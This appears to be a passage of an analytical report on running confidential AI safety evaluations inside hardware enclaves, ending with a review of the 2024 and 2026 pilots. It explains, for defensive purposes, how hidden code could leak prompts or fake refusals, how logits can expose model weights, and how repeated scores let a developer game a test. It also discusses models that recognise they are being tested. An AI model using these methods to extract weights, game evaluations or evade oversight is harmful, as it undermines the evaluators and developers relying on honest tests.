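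The weights file can contain code too. PyTorch has long saved models in Python's pickle format, which stores instructions for rebuilding an object, and those instructions can call almost any function on the machine. A developer could submit harmless inference code and hide code that leaks the tests in the weights file, which the evaluator never sees. The parties can prevent this by requiring a format such as safetensors, which holds only numbers and a description of their layout.

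Hidden code can also falsify results using only permitted steps, such as ordinary comparison and selection. For example, it could recognise prompts about nerve agents and replace the model's answers with refusals. Trask and colleagues write that redaction gives the parties confidence in both privacy and veracity. The claim about veracity is too strong for the hidden part, because attestation would prove only that the approved code ran, even if that code falsified the results.

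Hidden code can put secrets into outputs that the release rule permits. For example, an evaluator's scoring code could encode three of the model's 16-bit weights in a score with 15 decimal places.

### Using software to check hidden code

*Confidential Attestation* (Liu, Meng and colleagues, 2020) describes an alternative to allow-lists for checking code that the other side isn't allowed to read. The code's owner compiles it with a special compiler, which inserts a short safety check before every risky operation, such as writing to memory. Nobody has to trust the compiler, because a small public program inside the enclave follows the paths through the compiled code and confirms that every check is in place. If one is missing, the secret code doesn't run.

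The public program has only about 2,000 lines, so both sides can read it. The inserted checks slowed programs by 20 percent on average, or by about 10 percent without the checks against side channels. But the system works on compiled programs for Intel's SGX, not on GPU code, so it wouldn't cover the 8-billion-parameter model's main computation. It could cover the evaluator's scoring program if that program were written in a language such as C.

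*Attestable Audit* proposes running ordinary code-checking tools on the secret source inside an enclave. The enclave signs a report containing the hash of the source, the tools' settings and their results. The evaluator checks that this hash matches the one in the report from the attested build, and that the build's measurement matches that of the running program. If both match, the code that passed the audit is the code that is running. A prototype ran the audit with Bandit, a tool that searches Python programs for security problems. Since a developer could run many audits and show only the favourable ones, the evaluator should specify the tools and settings in advance.

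The reliability of the verdict depends on the tool. An AI reviewer may be better than Bandit, especially if it knows what to look for. In Anthropic's tests, Claude Mythos 5 found 11 of the 21 known bugs from the source code alone, and 20 when the researchers also told it which rule the code was supposed to follow. An evaluator can supply the rule that no prompt may leave the enclave.

There are two reasons to discount these results. First, some models remembered many of the older bugs from their training. Claude Mythos 5.2 found 15 of the 21 bugs from the source code alone, but only five of the nine that no model could recall. Second, the bugs were accidental. Because the audit's settings are public, a developer who wanted to hide a leak deliberately could run the same AI reviewer privately and rewrite the code until it passed.

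### Leaving hidden code no way out

The parties can instead assume that the hidden code is hostile and confine it. A sandbox around the inference program restricts it to receiving prompts and returning answers. If the program gets past the allow-list through a faulty library or a weights file, it still has to break out of the sandbox. A separate sandbox around the evaluation code lets it see the answers but not the weights. The software that enforces the sandboxes has to be open to both sides, and it becomes part of the trusted computing base.

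Neither sandbox needs a network connection. The enclave needs one to receive the secrets and deliver the score, but a small public program can control that connection and forward only what the release rule allows. Trask and colleagues would also remove keyboard, mouse and screen support from the operating system.

Deleting all stored data after the run prevents hidden code from saving the prompts and leaking them in a later run with looser rules. Hidden code could also store one prompt and work it into the answer to another, which matters if the developer can see some of the answers. Restarting the inference program before each prompt would prevent this. However, even on a B300, transferring 16 gigabytes takes a second and a half, so reloading 1,000 times would add at least 25 minutes.

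A good sandbox with no network leaves the hidden code nowhere to send data, whichever functions it calls. The allow-list adds protection by limiting the functions that the code can use to attack the sandbox. If the code is too unusual for an allow-list, the evaluator depends on the sandbox alone. Neither the allow-list nor the sandbox prevents dishonest answers.

### Public code, redacted code or an outside reviewer

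For the 8-billion-parameter model, public inference code is probably the best choice. The developer supplies the weights and a settings file, and a well-known program such as vLLM runs them. The evaluator can read all the code, so there is no hidden code that could copy prompts or fake refusals. The developer has to reveal the architecture, but this gives away little if the model resembles published ones such as Llama 3 8B. But the product may behave differently from the tested model if the developer's own program adds filters or selects words differently.

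Redaction suits a developer whose secrets are a few components written in a standard library, or an evaluator who is willing to show how the prompts reach the model but not how the scoring works. However, each party is less able to tell whether the test is run honestly as the other hides more code.

A developer with a lot of custom code may do better with an outside reviewer, who reads all of it under a confidentiality agreement and publishes the hash of the version they approved. Unlike an allow-list, a careful reviewer can notice code that singles out dangerous prompts. The reviewer needs neither the weights nor the prompts, so thieves have less to gain by targeting the reviewer than by targeting a third party who holds both. *AGAPECert* (2022), a system that issues certificates based on private data, has a similar arrangement. Before the code enters the enclave, it needs approval from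 a regulator and from either the data's owner or a service provider the owner trusts.

Reviewers can miss things, and each new version of the code needs another review. Trask and colleagues say that legal agreements and code review now delay these tests more than computing does. An evaluator who expects to test a developer's models regularly should therefore ask for the same inference code each time, so that only the weights change and the reviewer doesn't have to start again.

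## Deciding what may leave the enclave

Code that runs exactly as agreed can still reveal a secret if the agreed result contains too much information. A release rule therefore has to limit how much information leaves the enclave as well as its format. The parties can set one limit on how many bits the evaluator could learn about the weights and another on how many the developer could learn about the test. *Flexible Hardware-Enabled Guarantees for AI Compute* (2025), a proposal for security devices on AI hardware, describes a very strict limit under which each side learns only the final result, but many evaluators need more than that.

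### Counting the bits

A message that can take N different forms carries at most log₂ N bits. The number of safe answers to 1,000 prompts can be anything from 0 to 1,000, so it carries at most log₂ 1,001 bits, or about 10. A list of pass or fail results for all the prompts carries up to 1,000 bits.

Full answers are much larger. If a language model picks each token from a vocabulary of 200,000 entries, each token carries up to log₂ 200,000 ≈ 17.6 bits, and 1,000 answers of 500 tokens carry up to about 1.1 megabytes. Activations are far larger. A layer that is 4,096 values wide, with 16 bits per value, produces 8,192 bytes per token, or about 4.1 gigabytes for the 500,000 tokens of the answers.

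| What leaves the enclave | Most it can carry | Compared with 16 GB of weights |
|---|---|---|
| One total | 10 bits | One part in 13 billion |
| Five totals, for hazard categories of 200 prompts each | 38 bits | One part in 3.3 billion |
| Pass or fail for each prompt | 1,000 bits | One part in 128 million |
| Full answers | 1.1 MB | One part in 14,500 |
| Activations from one layer | 4.1 GB | About a quarter |
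| Key-value cache for the answers | 66 GB | About 4 times as large |
| Scores for every possible next token | 200 GB | 12.5 times as large |

These figures are upper limits, not estimates of what anyone could reconstruct. If the model answers 80 percent of the prompts safely, the pass-or-fail results carry only about 722 bits, because an observer could guess most of them. The results also describe only the model's behavior on 1,000 prompts, which reveals almost nothing about any particular weight. Likewise, an evaluator who has 4.1 gigabytes of activations does not have a quarter of the model's weights, even though the activations take up about a quarter as much space.

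Even a small budget can leak something valuable, such as the key to the developer's encrypted weights, which is typically 256 bits long. Hostile evaluation code that obtained the key could encode it in 256 of the pass-or-fail results, or in 26 totals from separate runs. Anyone who had recorded the encrypted file on its way to the enclave could then read all 16 gigabytes. The program that decrypts the weights should therefore erase the key before any evaluation code starts.

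Releasing the score as a whole number between 0 and 1,000 leaves no decimal places in which to hide data, but malicious scoring code could still encode a message in a false score.

The developer could learn a lot about the prompts from the model's full answers. For example, a model that refuses to explain how to grow a certain bacterium will often name the bacterium in its refusal. The developer should therefore not receive the answers. According to OpenMined, Google DeepMind could not see the prompts or the answers in the 2026 pilot.

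### What token probabilities reveal about the model

Some tests score a model on the probabilities it assigns to possible next tokens instead of on the text it writes. *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model* (Carlini et al., 2024) showed that these probabilities can expose some of the weights.

In its last step, a language model multiplies a hidden list of h numbers, g(x), by a matrix W with one row for each of the l tokens in the vocabulary:

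z = W · g(x).

The result z contains a score, called a logit, for each possible next token. The softmax function turns these scores into probabilities. In the example, l is 200,000 and h is 4,096, so each z contains 200,000 numbers, but only 4,096 of them can vary independently.

An attacker who collects the logits for more than 4,096 different prompts can put them side by side in a table, Q. Since Q = W · G, where G contains the hidden lists, a standard calculation called singular value decomposition can find how many independent directions Q has. That number is h, the width of the model. The same calculation also yields W multiplied by an unknown h × h matrix.

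Commercial APIs did not return full lists of logits, but some returned probabilities for the few most likely tokens and let customers raise the score of any token. An attacker could work out the full list by pushing one token after another into the top few. Carlini and colleagues extracted the final matrix of two small OpenAI models, Ada and Babbage, for under $20 and found widths of 1,024 and 2,048. OpenAI and Google then changed their APIs to make the attack harder.

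A careless release rule could make the attack easy again. In the example, W has 819 million entries, about a tenth of the model. A test that released the logits for 500,000 tokens would supply far more data than the attack needs, though the evaluator would still lack the other nine-tenths of the model. There is seldom a good reason to release logits, because the evaluation code can use them inside the enclave and send out only the score.

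*Beyond Attestation* (Das, 2026) extends the concern to cached intermediate state and to embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent pieces of text. It is an independent inventor's draft and has no standing as an internet standard. The sizes in the table support its point about cached state, because the key-value cache for a single test would be four times the size of the model.

### What repeated scores reveal about the test

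A developer that never sees a prompt can still tailor a model to the test if it gets a score after every change. This could happen under a scheme suggested in *Flexible Hardware-Enabled Guarantees for AI Compute*, in which a developer proves that it ran certain automated evaluations at regular intervals during training. If the developer saw all the scores and every run used the same prompts, it could keep whichever changes happened to suit those prompts.

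A developer that sees its score after each run can deliberately raise it without improving its model. Suppose the 1,000 prompts are yes-or-no questions and the developer's hidden code ignores their meaning. Instead, it hashes each question together with a number chosen for that run and answers yes if the hash is even, so each run uses a different guessing rule. Each rule gets about 500 questions right, but by chance the total differs from 500 by about 13 on average. The developer keeps the rules that scored above 500 and reverses those that scored below. After 100 runs, it submits a program that answers by majority vote among the 100 rules. The program will get about 60 percent of these questions right, but only about 50 percent of new ones.

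The attack becomes much stronger if the developer sees pass-or-fail results for each question. The developer could then calculate how much weight to give each guessing rule, and about 550 runs would be enough to get every question right. With totals alone, a majority vote after 550 runs would get about 72 percent right.

Organisers of machine learning competitions met this problem long before anyone tested language models in enclaves. Blum and Hardt (2015), in *The Ladder*, criticise the usual defences, such as rounding scores and limiting how often people can resubmit, as "poorly understood heuristics". They propose an algorithm that reports a new score only if it clearly beats the best one so far. If Sₜ is the true score of run t and η is the smallest improvement worth reporting, the leaderboard shows

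Rₜ = Sₜ rounded to the nearest multiple of η, if Sₜ > Rₜ₋₁ + η;
Rₜ = Rₜ₋₁ otherwise.

With η set at 5 percentage points, the posted score can take only 21 values and never falls. Over 100 runs, the posted scores can carry at most about 75 bits in total, compared with nearly 1,000 bits for 100 exact totals. The table shows how well the guessing attack would work against this defence and two simpler ones.

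| What the developer receives after each run | Final score of the guesses after 100 runs |
|---|---|
| Exact total | About 60% |
| Total rounded to the nearest 5 percentage points | About 59% |
| Total with random noise, typically 14 prompts up or down | About 58% |
| Ladder with η = 5 percentage points | Usually about 50% |

Rounding achieves little because it hides only the runs that scored close to 500, and the developer learns most from the runs that scored unusually high or low. The Ladder works because fewer than one guessed run in 1,000 beats a posted score of 50 percent by more than 5 percentage points.

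The noise in the table follows differential privacy, a standard method which requires that swapping one prompt for another change the probability of any output by a factor of at most e^ε. A smaller ε means more privacy. One prompt can change the total by at most 1, so the enclave can meet this requirement by adding noise from a Laplace distribution with scale 1/ε. With ε = 0.1, the noise is about as large as the chance variation in an 80 percent score. But the privacy losses add up, so after 100 runs ε is 10 and the factor is about 22,000, too large to guarantee much privacy.

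Blum and Hardt tested the Ladder on real submissions to a competition on Kaggle, a website that hosts such contests, and proved that it works even when participants adapt to earlier scores. But a participant can get round it by using several accounts. *Toward a Better Understanding of Leaderboard* (2015) finds that keeping the error below ε (here the error in the score, not the privacy measure) takes on the order of M/ε³ test items, where M is the number of accounts. Leaving aside constants and logarithms, 1,000 prompts correspond to an error of 10 percentage points with one account and 30 with 27 accounts. The formula shows only how the required number of items grows, but it suggests that 1,000 prompts are too few for a strong theoretical guarantee.

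A safety test should show when a new version of the model is less safe than the last, but under the Ladder the posted score stays the same in that case. The evaluator should therefore receive every exact total, and the developer should receive the Ladder's score instead. Since the enclave deletes its data after each run, the evaluator would also have to supply the previous best score as an input.

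For most confidential tests, a strict limit on runs is simpler and more effective than rounding or noise. Five runs would raise the guesses only to about 52 percent. The evaluator can also use fresh prompts for each version, but this uses up the supply of prompts. Splitting the 1,000 prompts into four sets of 250 would double the standard error of an 80 percent score, from about 1.3 to 2.5 percentage points. If the test is meant for publication rather than to help the developer improve the model, the best remedy is to send the score only to the evaluator until the developer has committed to a release version.

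### Logs, error messages and traffic

A program's logs often reveal more than its results. If the scoring program fails to read an answer, it may print the answer in an error message to help a programmer find the fault. In a confidential test, that message could expose a secret prompt or a dangerous answer to whoever collects the logs.

Faults inside an enclave are hard to find because, as Pattern Labs and Anthropic point out, enclaves disable breakpoints, traces and counters, the normal tools for watching a program run. It is safer for the parties to find most faults beforehand with mock assets and agree on a short list of error codes for the real run than to allow detailed logs, as programmers will be tempted to do. One code from a list of eight carries only 3 bits. A count of the answers that the scoring program could not read would add about 10 more, but it would help the evaluator judge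 how far to trust the score.

A crash can also leak information. Hidden evaluation code could crash on purpose if a certain weight is positive, which would reveal one bit. If failed runs don't count towards the limit, the evaluator could repeat this as often as it liked. Every run that receives the real weights or prompts should therefore count, even if it produces no score.

Usage reports can come close to revealing the result of each test item. Tinfoil's *Security and Privacy FAQ* says the company's system sends token counts out of the enclave for billing, but no content from requests or responses. That is reasonable for an ordinary customer, but in a safety test a refusal may take 20 tokens and a full set of dangerous instructions 500, so a separate count for each answer would show which prompts probably got past the model's defences. A thousand such counts carry up to about 9,000 bits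 of information. A single count for the whole run would be enough to calculate the bill.

Encryption hides what a message contains, but not when it was sent or, unless the sender pads it with meaningless data, how long it is. If the evaluator received the answers over the network one token at a time, an eavesdropper could count the tokens and might learn the length of each one. A confidential test avoids most of this because the model and the scoring program run on the same machine. The enclave can pad the final message to a fixed size.

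Whoever controls the host can observe more than an eavesdropper on the network. They can't read the tokens that pass through the bounce buffer between the GPU and the processor, but they can see each transfer. If the model answers one prompt at a time, they can probably work out the length of every answer. Running many prompts together makes this harder, because one transfer then carries tokens for many answers. This precaution matters more when the developer owns the host.

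The timing of the result can also carry a message. By choosing which second of a 17-minute window to finish in, hidden code can send 10 bits, as many as the score carries. The parties can prevent this by releasing the result at a fixed time, such as the next full hour.

The small public program that controls the enclave's network connection should enforce all these limits. MIRI's *A system overview for near term low trust AI compute verification* recommends separating the hardware that does the heavy computing from small trusted components that compare data and control what information leaves. In the example, the public program would accept only a whole number from 0 to 1,000 or one of the eight error codes. It could then pad the message, wait for the agreed time and send it to the agreed recipients. Tlaie and Farrell also discuss limits on rate and bandwidth, which would slow any leak that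 the other rules missed.

### Why evaluators want to look inside the model

A model's answers may be misleading if it recognises that it is being tested. Sometimes it mentions the test in its chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before it answers, but it may also behave differently without mentioning it. Apollo Research (2026), which tests models for deceptive behaviour, argues that outside evaluators need white-box access to deal with both cases. It warns that without deeper access, governments and outside evaluators may soon struggle to support rigorous claims about loss of control.

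One method is steering, which changes the model's activations while it runs. Researchers first look for a direction v in the activations that corresponds to recognising a test. They might take the average activations on prompts that look like tests and subtract the average on prompts that look like ordinary use. During the real test they replace each activation h with

h′ = h − αv,

where α sets the strength of the change. *Balancing rigor and utility*, an essay on the forum LessWrong, recounts that Anthropic used this method on Claude Sonnet 4.5 and that its misalignment score rose from 0 to 8 percent.

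The result suggests that the score of zero was misleadingly good, but it doesn't prove that the model had been hiding its behaviour. Changing a model's activations can damage its judgement in other ways. An evaluator could check for this by subtracting random directions of the same size and seeing whether the score rises as much.

Steering doesn't require the activations to leave the enclave. An evaluator that already has a suitable direction v could run the 1,000 prompts once normally and once with steering, then release two totals, which together carry at most 20 bits. A test for a known pattern in the activations can similarly give one yes or no per answer. Both tests use the model's internals but release very little information.

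This works only if the evaluator knows what to look for. According to *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations*, outside testing can't reliably find suppressed capabilities, covert mechanisms, or dangerous knowledge that the developer has not fully removed. An evaluator investigating these may need to compare many layers and follow up on whatever looks odd, which a fixed program with a 20-bit result doesn't allow.

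*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) reports a firm academic consensus that deeper access allows more outside scrutiny and that secure infrastructure can make that access possible. It also notes a gap between what infrastructure is possible and what is in use. *Developing a Framework for Secure Third-Party Access to Frontier AI* (Hurel, Glantz and Cuthbert, 2026) addresses the problem with a matrix of access and risk and a set of security controls. Google supported the taskforce behind the paper and has an interest in how much access such frameworks recommend.

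### Pour Demain's design for tests of internals

Pour Demain's 2026 design tries to give evaluators some of this freedom without giving them the weights. It combines confidential computing with an instrumentation interface and a controlled exit path, which *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations* calls "de facto glass-box" evaluation.

The instrumentation interface is a standard set of requests that the evaluator's code can make to the model. It returns signals for analysis but never the raw weights. McCann-Sayles and Verma list four kinds of request in Pour Demain's design:

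- Activation capture copies the numbers that a layer produces.
- Representation steering changes those numbers during a run.
- Expert-routing analysis applies to mixture-of-experts models and records which parts of the network process each token.
- Input gradients measure how strongly a small change in each part of the prompt would affect a chosen output.

The four can reveal very different amounts. If a layer sends each token to 8 of 256 experts, the choice carries at most 49 bits per token, compared with 65,536 bits for the activations of a layer 4,096 values wide. Gradients can be especially revealing. In the toy model y = w · x, the gradient of y with respect to x is w, so a single request would reveal every weight. Real language models are far more complicated, but the toy model shows why the interface should return a summary, such as one number per word of the prompt, instead of the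 full gradient.

The controlled exit path determines which of these signals can leave the enclave. *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations* describes it as a way to limit the risk that an evaluator extracts the model, and McCann-Sayles and Verma explain that its controls restrict and monitor what the evaluator exports. For the 8-billion-parameter model, the exit program could subtract the size of each signal from an agreed total and reject further requests once the total reached zero.

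The exit path has to control which points in the model an evaluator can observe together, as well as how much data leaves. Many of a language model's layers contain steps of the form y = Wx, where x and y are lists of numbers and W is a matrix of weights. If W had 4,096 rows and columns, an evaluator that captured both x and y for 4,096 suitable tokens could solve for W. About 67 megabytes of activations would then reveal nearly 17 million weights, apart from small rounding errors. The exit path also has to keep a record of earlier requests, so that nobody can collect x in one run and y in the next.

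The design includes a formal threat model, which sets out what attackers might try and what they can do, and an analysis of the remaining risks. One obvious threat to the developer is an evaluator that collects many small, permitted signals. McCann-Sayles and Verma add that even the size of the weights or of the serving code can be highly sensitive. The evaluator may fear that the developer will learn how the test works from the evaluator's requests. A log of requests for one layer and one type of prompt could reveal much about the method, so the monitoring should report how much of the budget the evaluator has used but not which requests it made.

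Three hosting layouts distribute trust differently so that as many developers as possible will take part. In each, the most important factor is who operates the machine. If the developer operates it, the weights stay on its premises, but it can watch the timing of the test and has physical access to the hardware. If the evaluator or a public body operates it, the developer has to send its encrypted weights to a building it doesn't control. A cloud company may be easier for both sides to accept if neither owns it.

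Only part of the design exists. *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations* rates the underlying confidential computing as "production-ready" but describes the instrumentation layer as a concrete design that still needs building and testing, and it proposes a limited pilot facility. Pour Demain has run GLM-5.1 in an enclave with vllm-lens and has demonstrated its access controls. Because the weights of GLM-5.1 are public, the run tested whether the method works, not whether a developer would trust it. The results McCann-Sayles and Verma report are about speed. A better test of the exit path would give a skilled team the permitted signals from a small model and measure how much of the model they could rebuild.

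### Choosing a release rule

For the example test, a single total sent to both sides is a good starting point. The evaluator should ask for the full answers if software can't score them reliably, as in the 2026 pilot, where the evaluator's staff judged the outputs. The developer gives up little by releasing the answers if the model is already on sale, since any customer can collect 1.1 megabytes of its answers. It gives up more if the model is unreleased or lacks its usual safety filters. Releasing raw internal signals is much harder to justify, and the evaluator should first try to analyze them inside the enclave.

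| Release rule | Most it can carry in one run | What it permits | Main risks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Total only | 10 bits | Publishing a score and comparing models | Errors in scoring are hard to find; repeated totals help the developer fit the test |
| Pass or fail for each prompt | 1,000 bits | Finding weak areas and checking whether two versions fail on the same prompts | There is room for an encryption key; a developer that sees repeated results can fit the test much faster |
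| Full answers to the evaluator only | 1.1 MB | Human judgement, correction of scoring errors and study of how the model fails | The evaluator holds dangerous text and could use it to train an imitation; a leak would reveal many of the prompts |
| Internal signals to the evaluator | 4.1 GB for one layer | Searching for hidden knowledge, hidden abilities and signs that the model recognises a test | Combined signals may reveal weights or architecture; the exit controls lack a published test against extraction |

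## The 2024 and 2026 pilots, step by step

Developers and outside evaluators have run the whole procedure together at least twice. In 2024 OpenMined rehearsed it with staff from Anthropic and the UK's AI Safety Institute (now the AI Security Institute), using public material in place of secrets. In 2026 Google DeepMind supplied a commercial model, and two evaluators tested it with prompts they kept secret.

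| Step | 2024 pilot | 2026 pilot |
|---|---|---|
| Developer | Anthropic staff | Google DeepMind |
| Evaluator | UK AI Safety Institute staff | AVERI, then the Singapore AI Safety Institute |
| Model | GPT-2 (public) | Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite (secret weights) |
| Test set | Five rows of CAMEL-bio (public) | Reserved AILuminate prompts, then a Singapore prompt set (both secret) |
| Host | Microsoft Azure | Google Cloud |
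| Hardware | Nvidia H100 with AMD SEV-SNP | Nvidia H100 with Intel TDX |
| Verification | Microsoft's and Nvidia's services | Google's services |
| Code review | Both sides approved all the code | Some of Google's code went in unreviewed |
| Who received the output | The researcher who started the run | The evaluator |
| Published figures | Time taken | None from the test itself |

### The models and the tests

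In the 2024 pilot, GPT-2 stood in for Anthropic's unreleased models, and CAMEL-bio, a public collection of biology problems with solutions, stood in for the institute's confidential tests. Each organisation stored its material on a Datasite, a PySyft server that controls who may use its contents. Trask and colleagues specify at least two machines per Datasite, each with 8 processors and 16 gigabytes of memory. Each side also uploaded a mock asset, although the real assets were already harmless stand-ins.

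The 2026 pilot used Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, whose weights and parameter count Google has not released. Trask and colleagues report that the weights entered the enclave uncompressed and that the machine had a single H100 with 80 gigabytes of memory. If all the weights were in the GPU's memory at 16 bits each, the model has fewer than 40 billion parameters. A developer that considers its model's size sensitive should therefore be careful about publishing the machine type.

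The non-profit AI Verification and Evaluation Research Institute (AVERI) took its prompts from AILuminate, a safety benchmark run by MLCommons, a consortium of companies and universities. MLCommons says version 1.1 has 12,000 public practice prompts and 12,000 hidden ones in each language, across 12 hazard categories. In an ordinary official test, the hidden prompts go to wherever the model is running, which may be the developer's own server. The pilot's prompts came from a separate reserve and covered weapons of mass destruction, explosives, cyberattacks, hate speech, self-harm and violent crime.

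Google could have known how AVERI would mark answers on this benchmark. MLCommons' *The Widening Gap Between AI Safety and AI Security* lists Google, Google DeepMind and AVERI as members of its working group on AI risk, and groups within that programme wrote the hazard definitions and the criteria for a bad answer. Outside suppliers provided the prompts under non-disclosure terms. Trask and colleagues say the prompts were "not shared broadly" with the members, which leaves open whether a few members saw some of them.

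The Singapore institute brought its own private prompts, designed to draw out content that would be harmful in Singapore. Trask and colleagues do not describe the prompts further.

### Setting up and verifying the enclave

The 2024 enclave was a container on Azure that exchanged data directly with the two Datasites. To connect them, one side had to propose a route, both had to approve it, and each had to change its firewall to admit the other's traffic. Security departments are usually reluctant to open new holes in a firewall, and OpenMined now lists avoiding this among the practical problems it has worked on.

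Trask and colleagues set out a procedure in 2026 in which each party connects to the enclave from a Python session. They suggest Google Colab as one place to run the session. Colab is a poor choice for anyone testing a Google model, because it normally runs on Google's servers, where the prompts would be readable before the PySyft client encrypted them. Trask and colleagues say that AVERI encrypted the prompts itself, but they don't say where it ran its session.

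Microsoft and Nvidia provided the attestation services for the 2024 pilot. Trask and colleagues point out that anyone could run such a service, but the parties would have to trust whoever did. Neither company was a party to the test, so at least neither side was checking its own machine.

The 2026 pilot had more to protect but a weaker check. It had neither independent verification nor reproducible builds, both of which Trask and colleagues recommend. Google, also the developer, signed and verified the report through its own services, and Trask and colleagues acknowledge that this requires more trust in Google. Outsiders have validated the build process for the guest operating system, which runs inside the virtual machine, but they can't reproduce its individual builds.

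Google publishes the expected measurements of its guest system. If AVERI compared them with the report, a match would have shown that the enclave was running a system Google had published for its customers, rather than one prepared for this test. A match would not have shown that the system was compiled from the public source code.

### Approving the code

The 2024 researchers wrote their code in Python and could import any package. The code only ran the model on the five rows, and staff on both sides read and signed all of it. Trask and colleagues left out more elaborate evaluation methods because others had already programmed them.

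In 2026, the parties could not review all the code without exposing Google's trade secrets. They could not check it against an allow-list instead, because Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite also uses Google's own routines, and Trask and colleagues judged that replacing them would be too large an engineering job for the project. Google told AVERI about these limits, and AVERI accepted the arrangement. The report doesn't mention whether the Singapore institute also knew and agreed.

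The unreviewed code matters because the model has to receive the prompts in readable form. Inside the enclave, Google's model server exchanged data with other programs through Unix domain sockets, which connect programs on the same machine without using a network. But a program that receives prompts through a socket may still be able to open its own network connection. Trask and colleagues do not describe a sandbox that would have prevented this.

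Google is unlikely to steal prompts deliberately during a pilot meant to show that it couldn't. An accidental leak is more likely, since Google's routines could, for example, write their inputs to a log. The method is supposed to remove that risk.

### Running the test

The 2024 pilot took 28 minutes and 3 seconds, from writing the code together to delivering the result, with everyone on the same call. Trask and colleagues report that moving the assets into the enclave, running the code and returning the result took 1 minute and 11 seconds, or about 4 percent of the total. They attribute that delay to immature software rather than to the enclave.

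The machine was bound to finish quickly because the test had only five rows and the model was small. A larger test would still take much more human time than machine time. At the speeds Wang and colleagues measured on an H100, the 8-billion-parameter model would write its 1,000 answers in about 161 seconds, a tenth of the nearly 27 minutes that people spent on the rest of the 2024 process.

A real test would probably take far longer than those 27 minutes. Both organisations had set up their servers before timing began, and nobody had a strong reason to search the code for leaks because both assets were public. Trask and colleagues also planned to judge the pilot by how long each organisation took to get internal approval, but they give no figure for this. Approval could easily take weeks if a company's lawyers and security staff had to decide whether to risk a commercial model.

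There are no timings for the 2026 pilot. Trask and colleagues cite the 2024 pilot when they blame most of the delay on people. The 2026 pilot could have provided much better evidence, because its participants had real secrets to protect and real legal agreements to negotiate.

### What came out

In 2024 only the researcher who had started the run received the result.

It is less clear what left the enclave in 2026. A diagram in the technical report shows the evaluator receiving "aggregate metrics", such as a total score, but according to the text, AVERI decrypted the model's answers and its staff judged them. The text is more specific, so it presumably describes what happened, while the diagram shows the general design. If so, AVERI received the full answers, which Google DeepMind could not see, and calculated any score outside the enclave.

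None of the three accounts by Google, OpenMined and their partners includes a score for Gemini. Isaac and colleagues refer readers to the technical report for the pilot's "findings", but the report contains no safety findings about the model. It also omits the number of prompts and runs, and the running time. OpenMined mentions further posts by AVERI and MLCommons, which may contain more.

The pilot was probably never meant to produce an official AILuminate grade. MLCommons awards one only after a model has answered the complete hidden set and MLCommons' private scoring system has judged the answers. AVERI used human judges and only a selection from the reserve. The selection was probably much smaller than 12,000, because marking that many answers at a minute each would take 200 hours.

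The size of that selection would greatly affect how to interpret a score. AILuminate's top grade requires that fewer than 0.1 percent of answers break the rules. If a model gave no bad answers to 1,000 prompts, its true rate of bad answers could still be as high as 0.3 percent, at 95 percent confidence. It would have to answer about 3,000 prompts without a bad answer to bring that limit down to 0.1 percent.

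Publishing a pilot of a method without the model's score is reasonable, particularly if the evaluator wants to keep its findings private. Omitting the prompt counts and running times is harder to justify, because they would have revealed little about the secret tests or weights, and other evaluators need them to plan their own tests.

### Which of the four properties the pilots showed

The table separates what each pilot showed from what its participants had to assume about each of the four properties a confidential evaluation aims for.

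| Property | 2024 pilot | 2026 pilot |
|---|---|---|
| The weights stay secret | Rehearsed with public weights; the evaluator could see the architecture | Shown in ordinary use against the evaluators; not tested against an outside host |
| The test set stays secret | Rehearsed with public data | Google's staff had no ordinary access; the rest depends on Google's unreviewed code and its attestation service |
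| The agreed computation runs | Largely shown, with full code review and outside attestation services | Partly assumed, because some code was closed to the evaluators |
| The published result comes from it | Not shown, because there was no published score | Not shown, for the same reason |

Neither pilot's report describes anyone trying to steal the weights or the prompts, so the evidence for secrecy is limited to the system working as designed in normal use. A leak through Google's hidden code might have gone unnoticed.

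In the 2026 pilot, the weights were better protected than the prompts. Google hosted the pilot and kept the weights on its own cloud, and AVERI and the Singapore institute never had access to them. The pilot therefore does not show that a developer would send its weights to a machine that someone else operates. Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite was also a less valuable secret than Google's largest models.

The third property covers the identity of the model as well as the code. Trask and colleagues do not mention a published hash of the weights, or any other way for the evaluators to confirm that they were testing the Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite that customers use. The evaluators could compare the model's answers to harmless prompts with those from Google's public service, but this would give only rough evidence.

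To show the fourth property, the pilot would have needed a signed output and a published result that readers could compare with it. Human marking complicates this, because an enclave can sign the answers but can't certify how AVERI's staff marked them afterwards. AVERI could publish a hash of the signed answers along with the score, so an auditor with access to the answers could later repeat the marking.

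### How far "first" is justified

The organisers of both pilots claimed a first, and the claim took several forms. In 2024 Trask and colleagues said theirs was, to their knowledge, the first practical test of H100 enclaves for AI evaluation across two organisations. This narrow claim is believable because there had been little opportunity to run such a test earlier. The H100 was the first GPU to support confidential computing, and they describe GPU enclaves as still in public beta at the time.

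The unqualified claim to the "world's first double-blind AI evaluations" in the title of Isaac and colleagues' announcement is too broad. MedPerf, another MLCommons project, tests medical AI models on patient data held by hospitals. Three weeks before the Gemini announcement, Mitchell (2026), in *Google Cloud & MLCommons launch secure MedPerf tests*, reported that MedPerf could run on Google's confidential computing service without exposing the data or the model's code. Trask and colleagues themselves mention that MedPerf has evaluated encrypted medical imaging models this way.

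MedPerf is also a counterexample to OpenMined's statement that every AI evaluation before the Gemini pilot made one side risk its secrets. TRUCE and *Attestable Audits* had already run benchmarks on language models in enclaves before the pilot, although those models' weights were public.

The body of the announcement limits the claim to a "proprietary, frontier class AI model". The technical report limits it further, to cases where two organisations keep secrets from each other, one its frontier-class weights and the other its closed benchmark, and adds "we believe". This narrower claim is probably right. The 2024 pilot used public assets, MedPerf tests medical models, and nobody seems to have published an earlier case that fits. A company could have run a similar test privately, but there is no evidence that one did.

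"Frontier class" is the most doubtful part. Epoch AI's *Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite (Jun 2025)* dates the preview version to 17 June 2025, 14 months before the announcement. Google sold Flash-Lite as the cheapest and fastest model in the 2.5 family. It was a commercial model from a leading developer, but not one of the most capable models of 2026. This matters for the method as well as the publicity, because the most capable models generally need several GPUs and the pilot used one.

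The 2026 report also comes from people with an interest in the pilot's success. Fifteen of its 30 authors list Google as an affiliation, including Trask, who also lists OpenMined. AVERI, MLCommons and the Singapore institute also have authors on the paper, so no outside group has yet published an assessment of the pilot. To its credit, the report discloses the unreviewed code, the builds that outsiders can't reproduce and Google's role in verification, most of which readers could not have discovered themselves.

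### Work since August 2026

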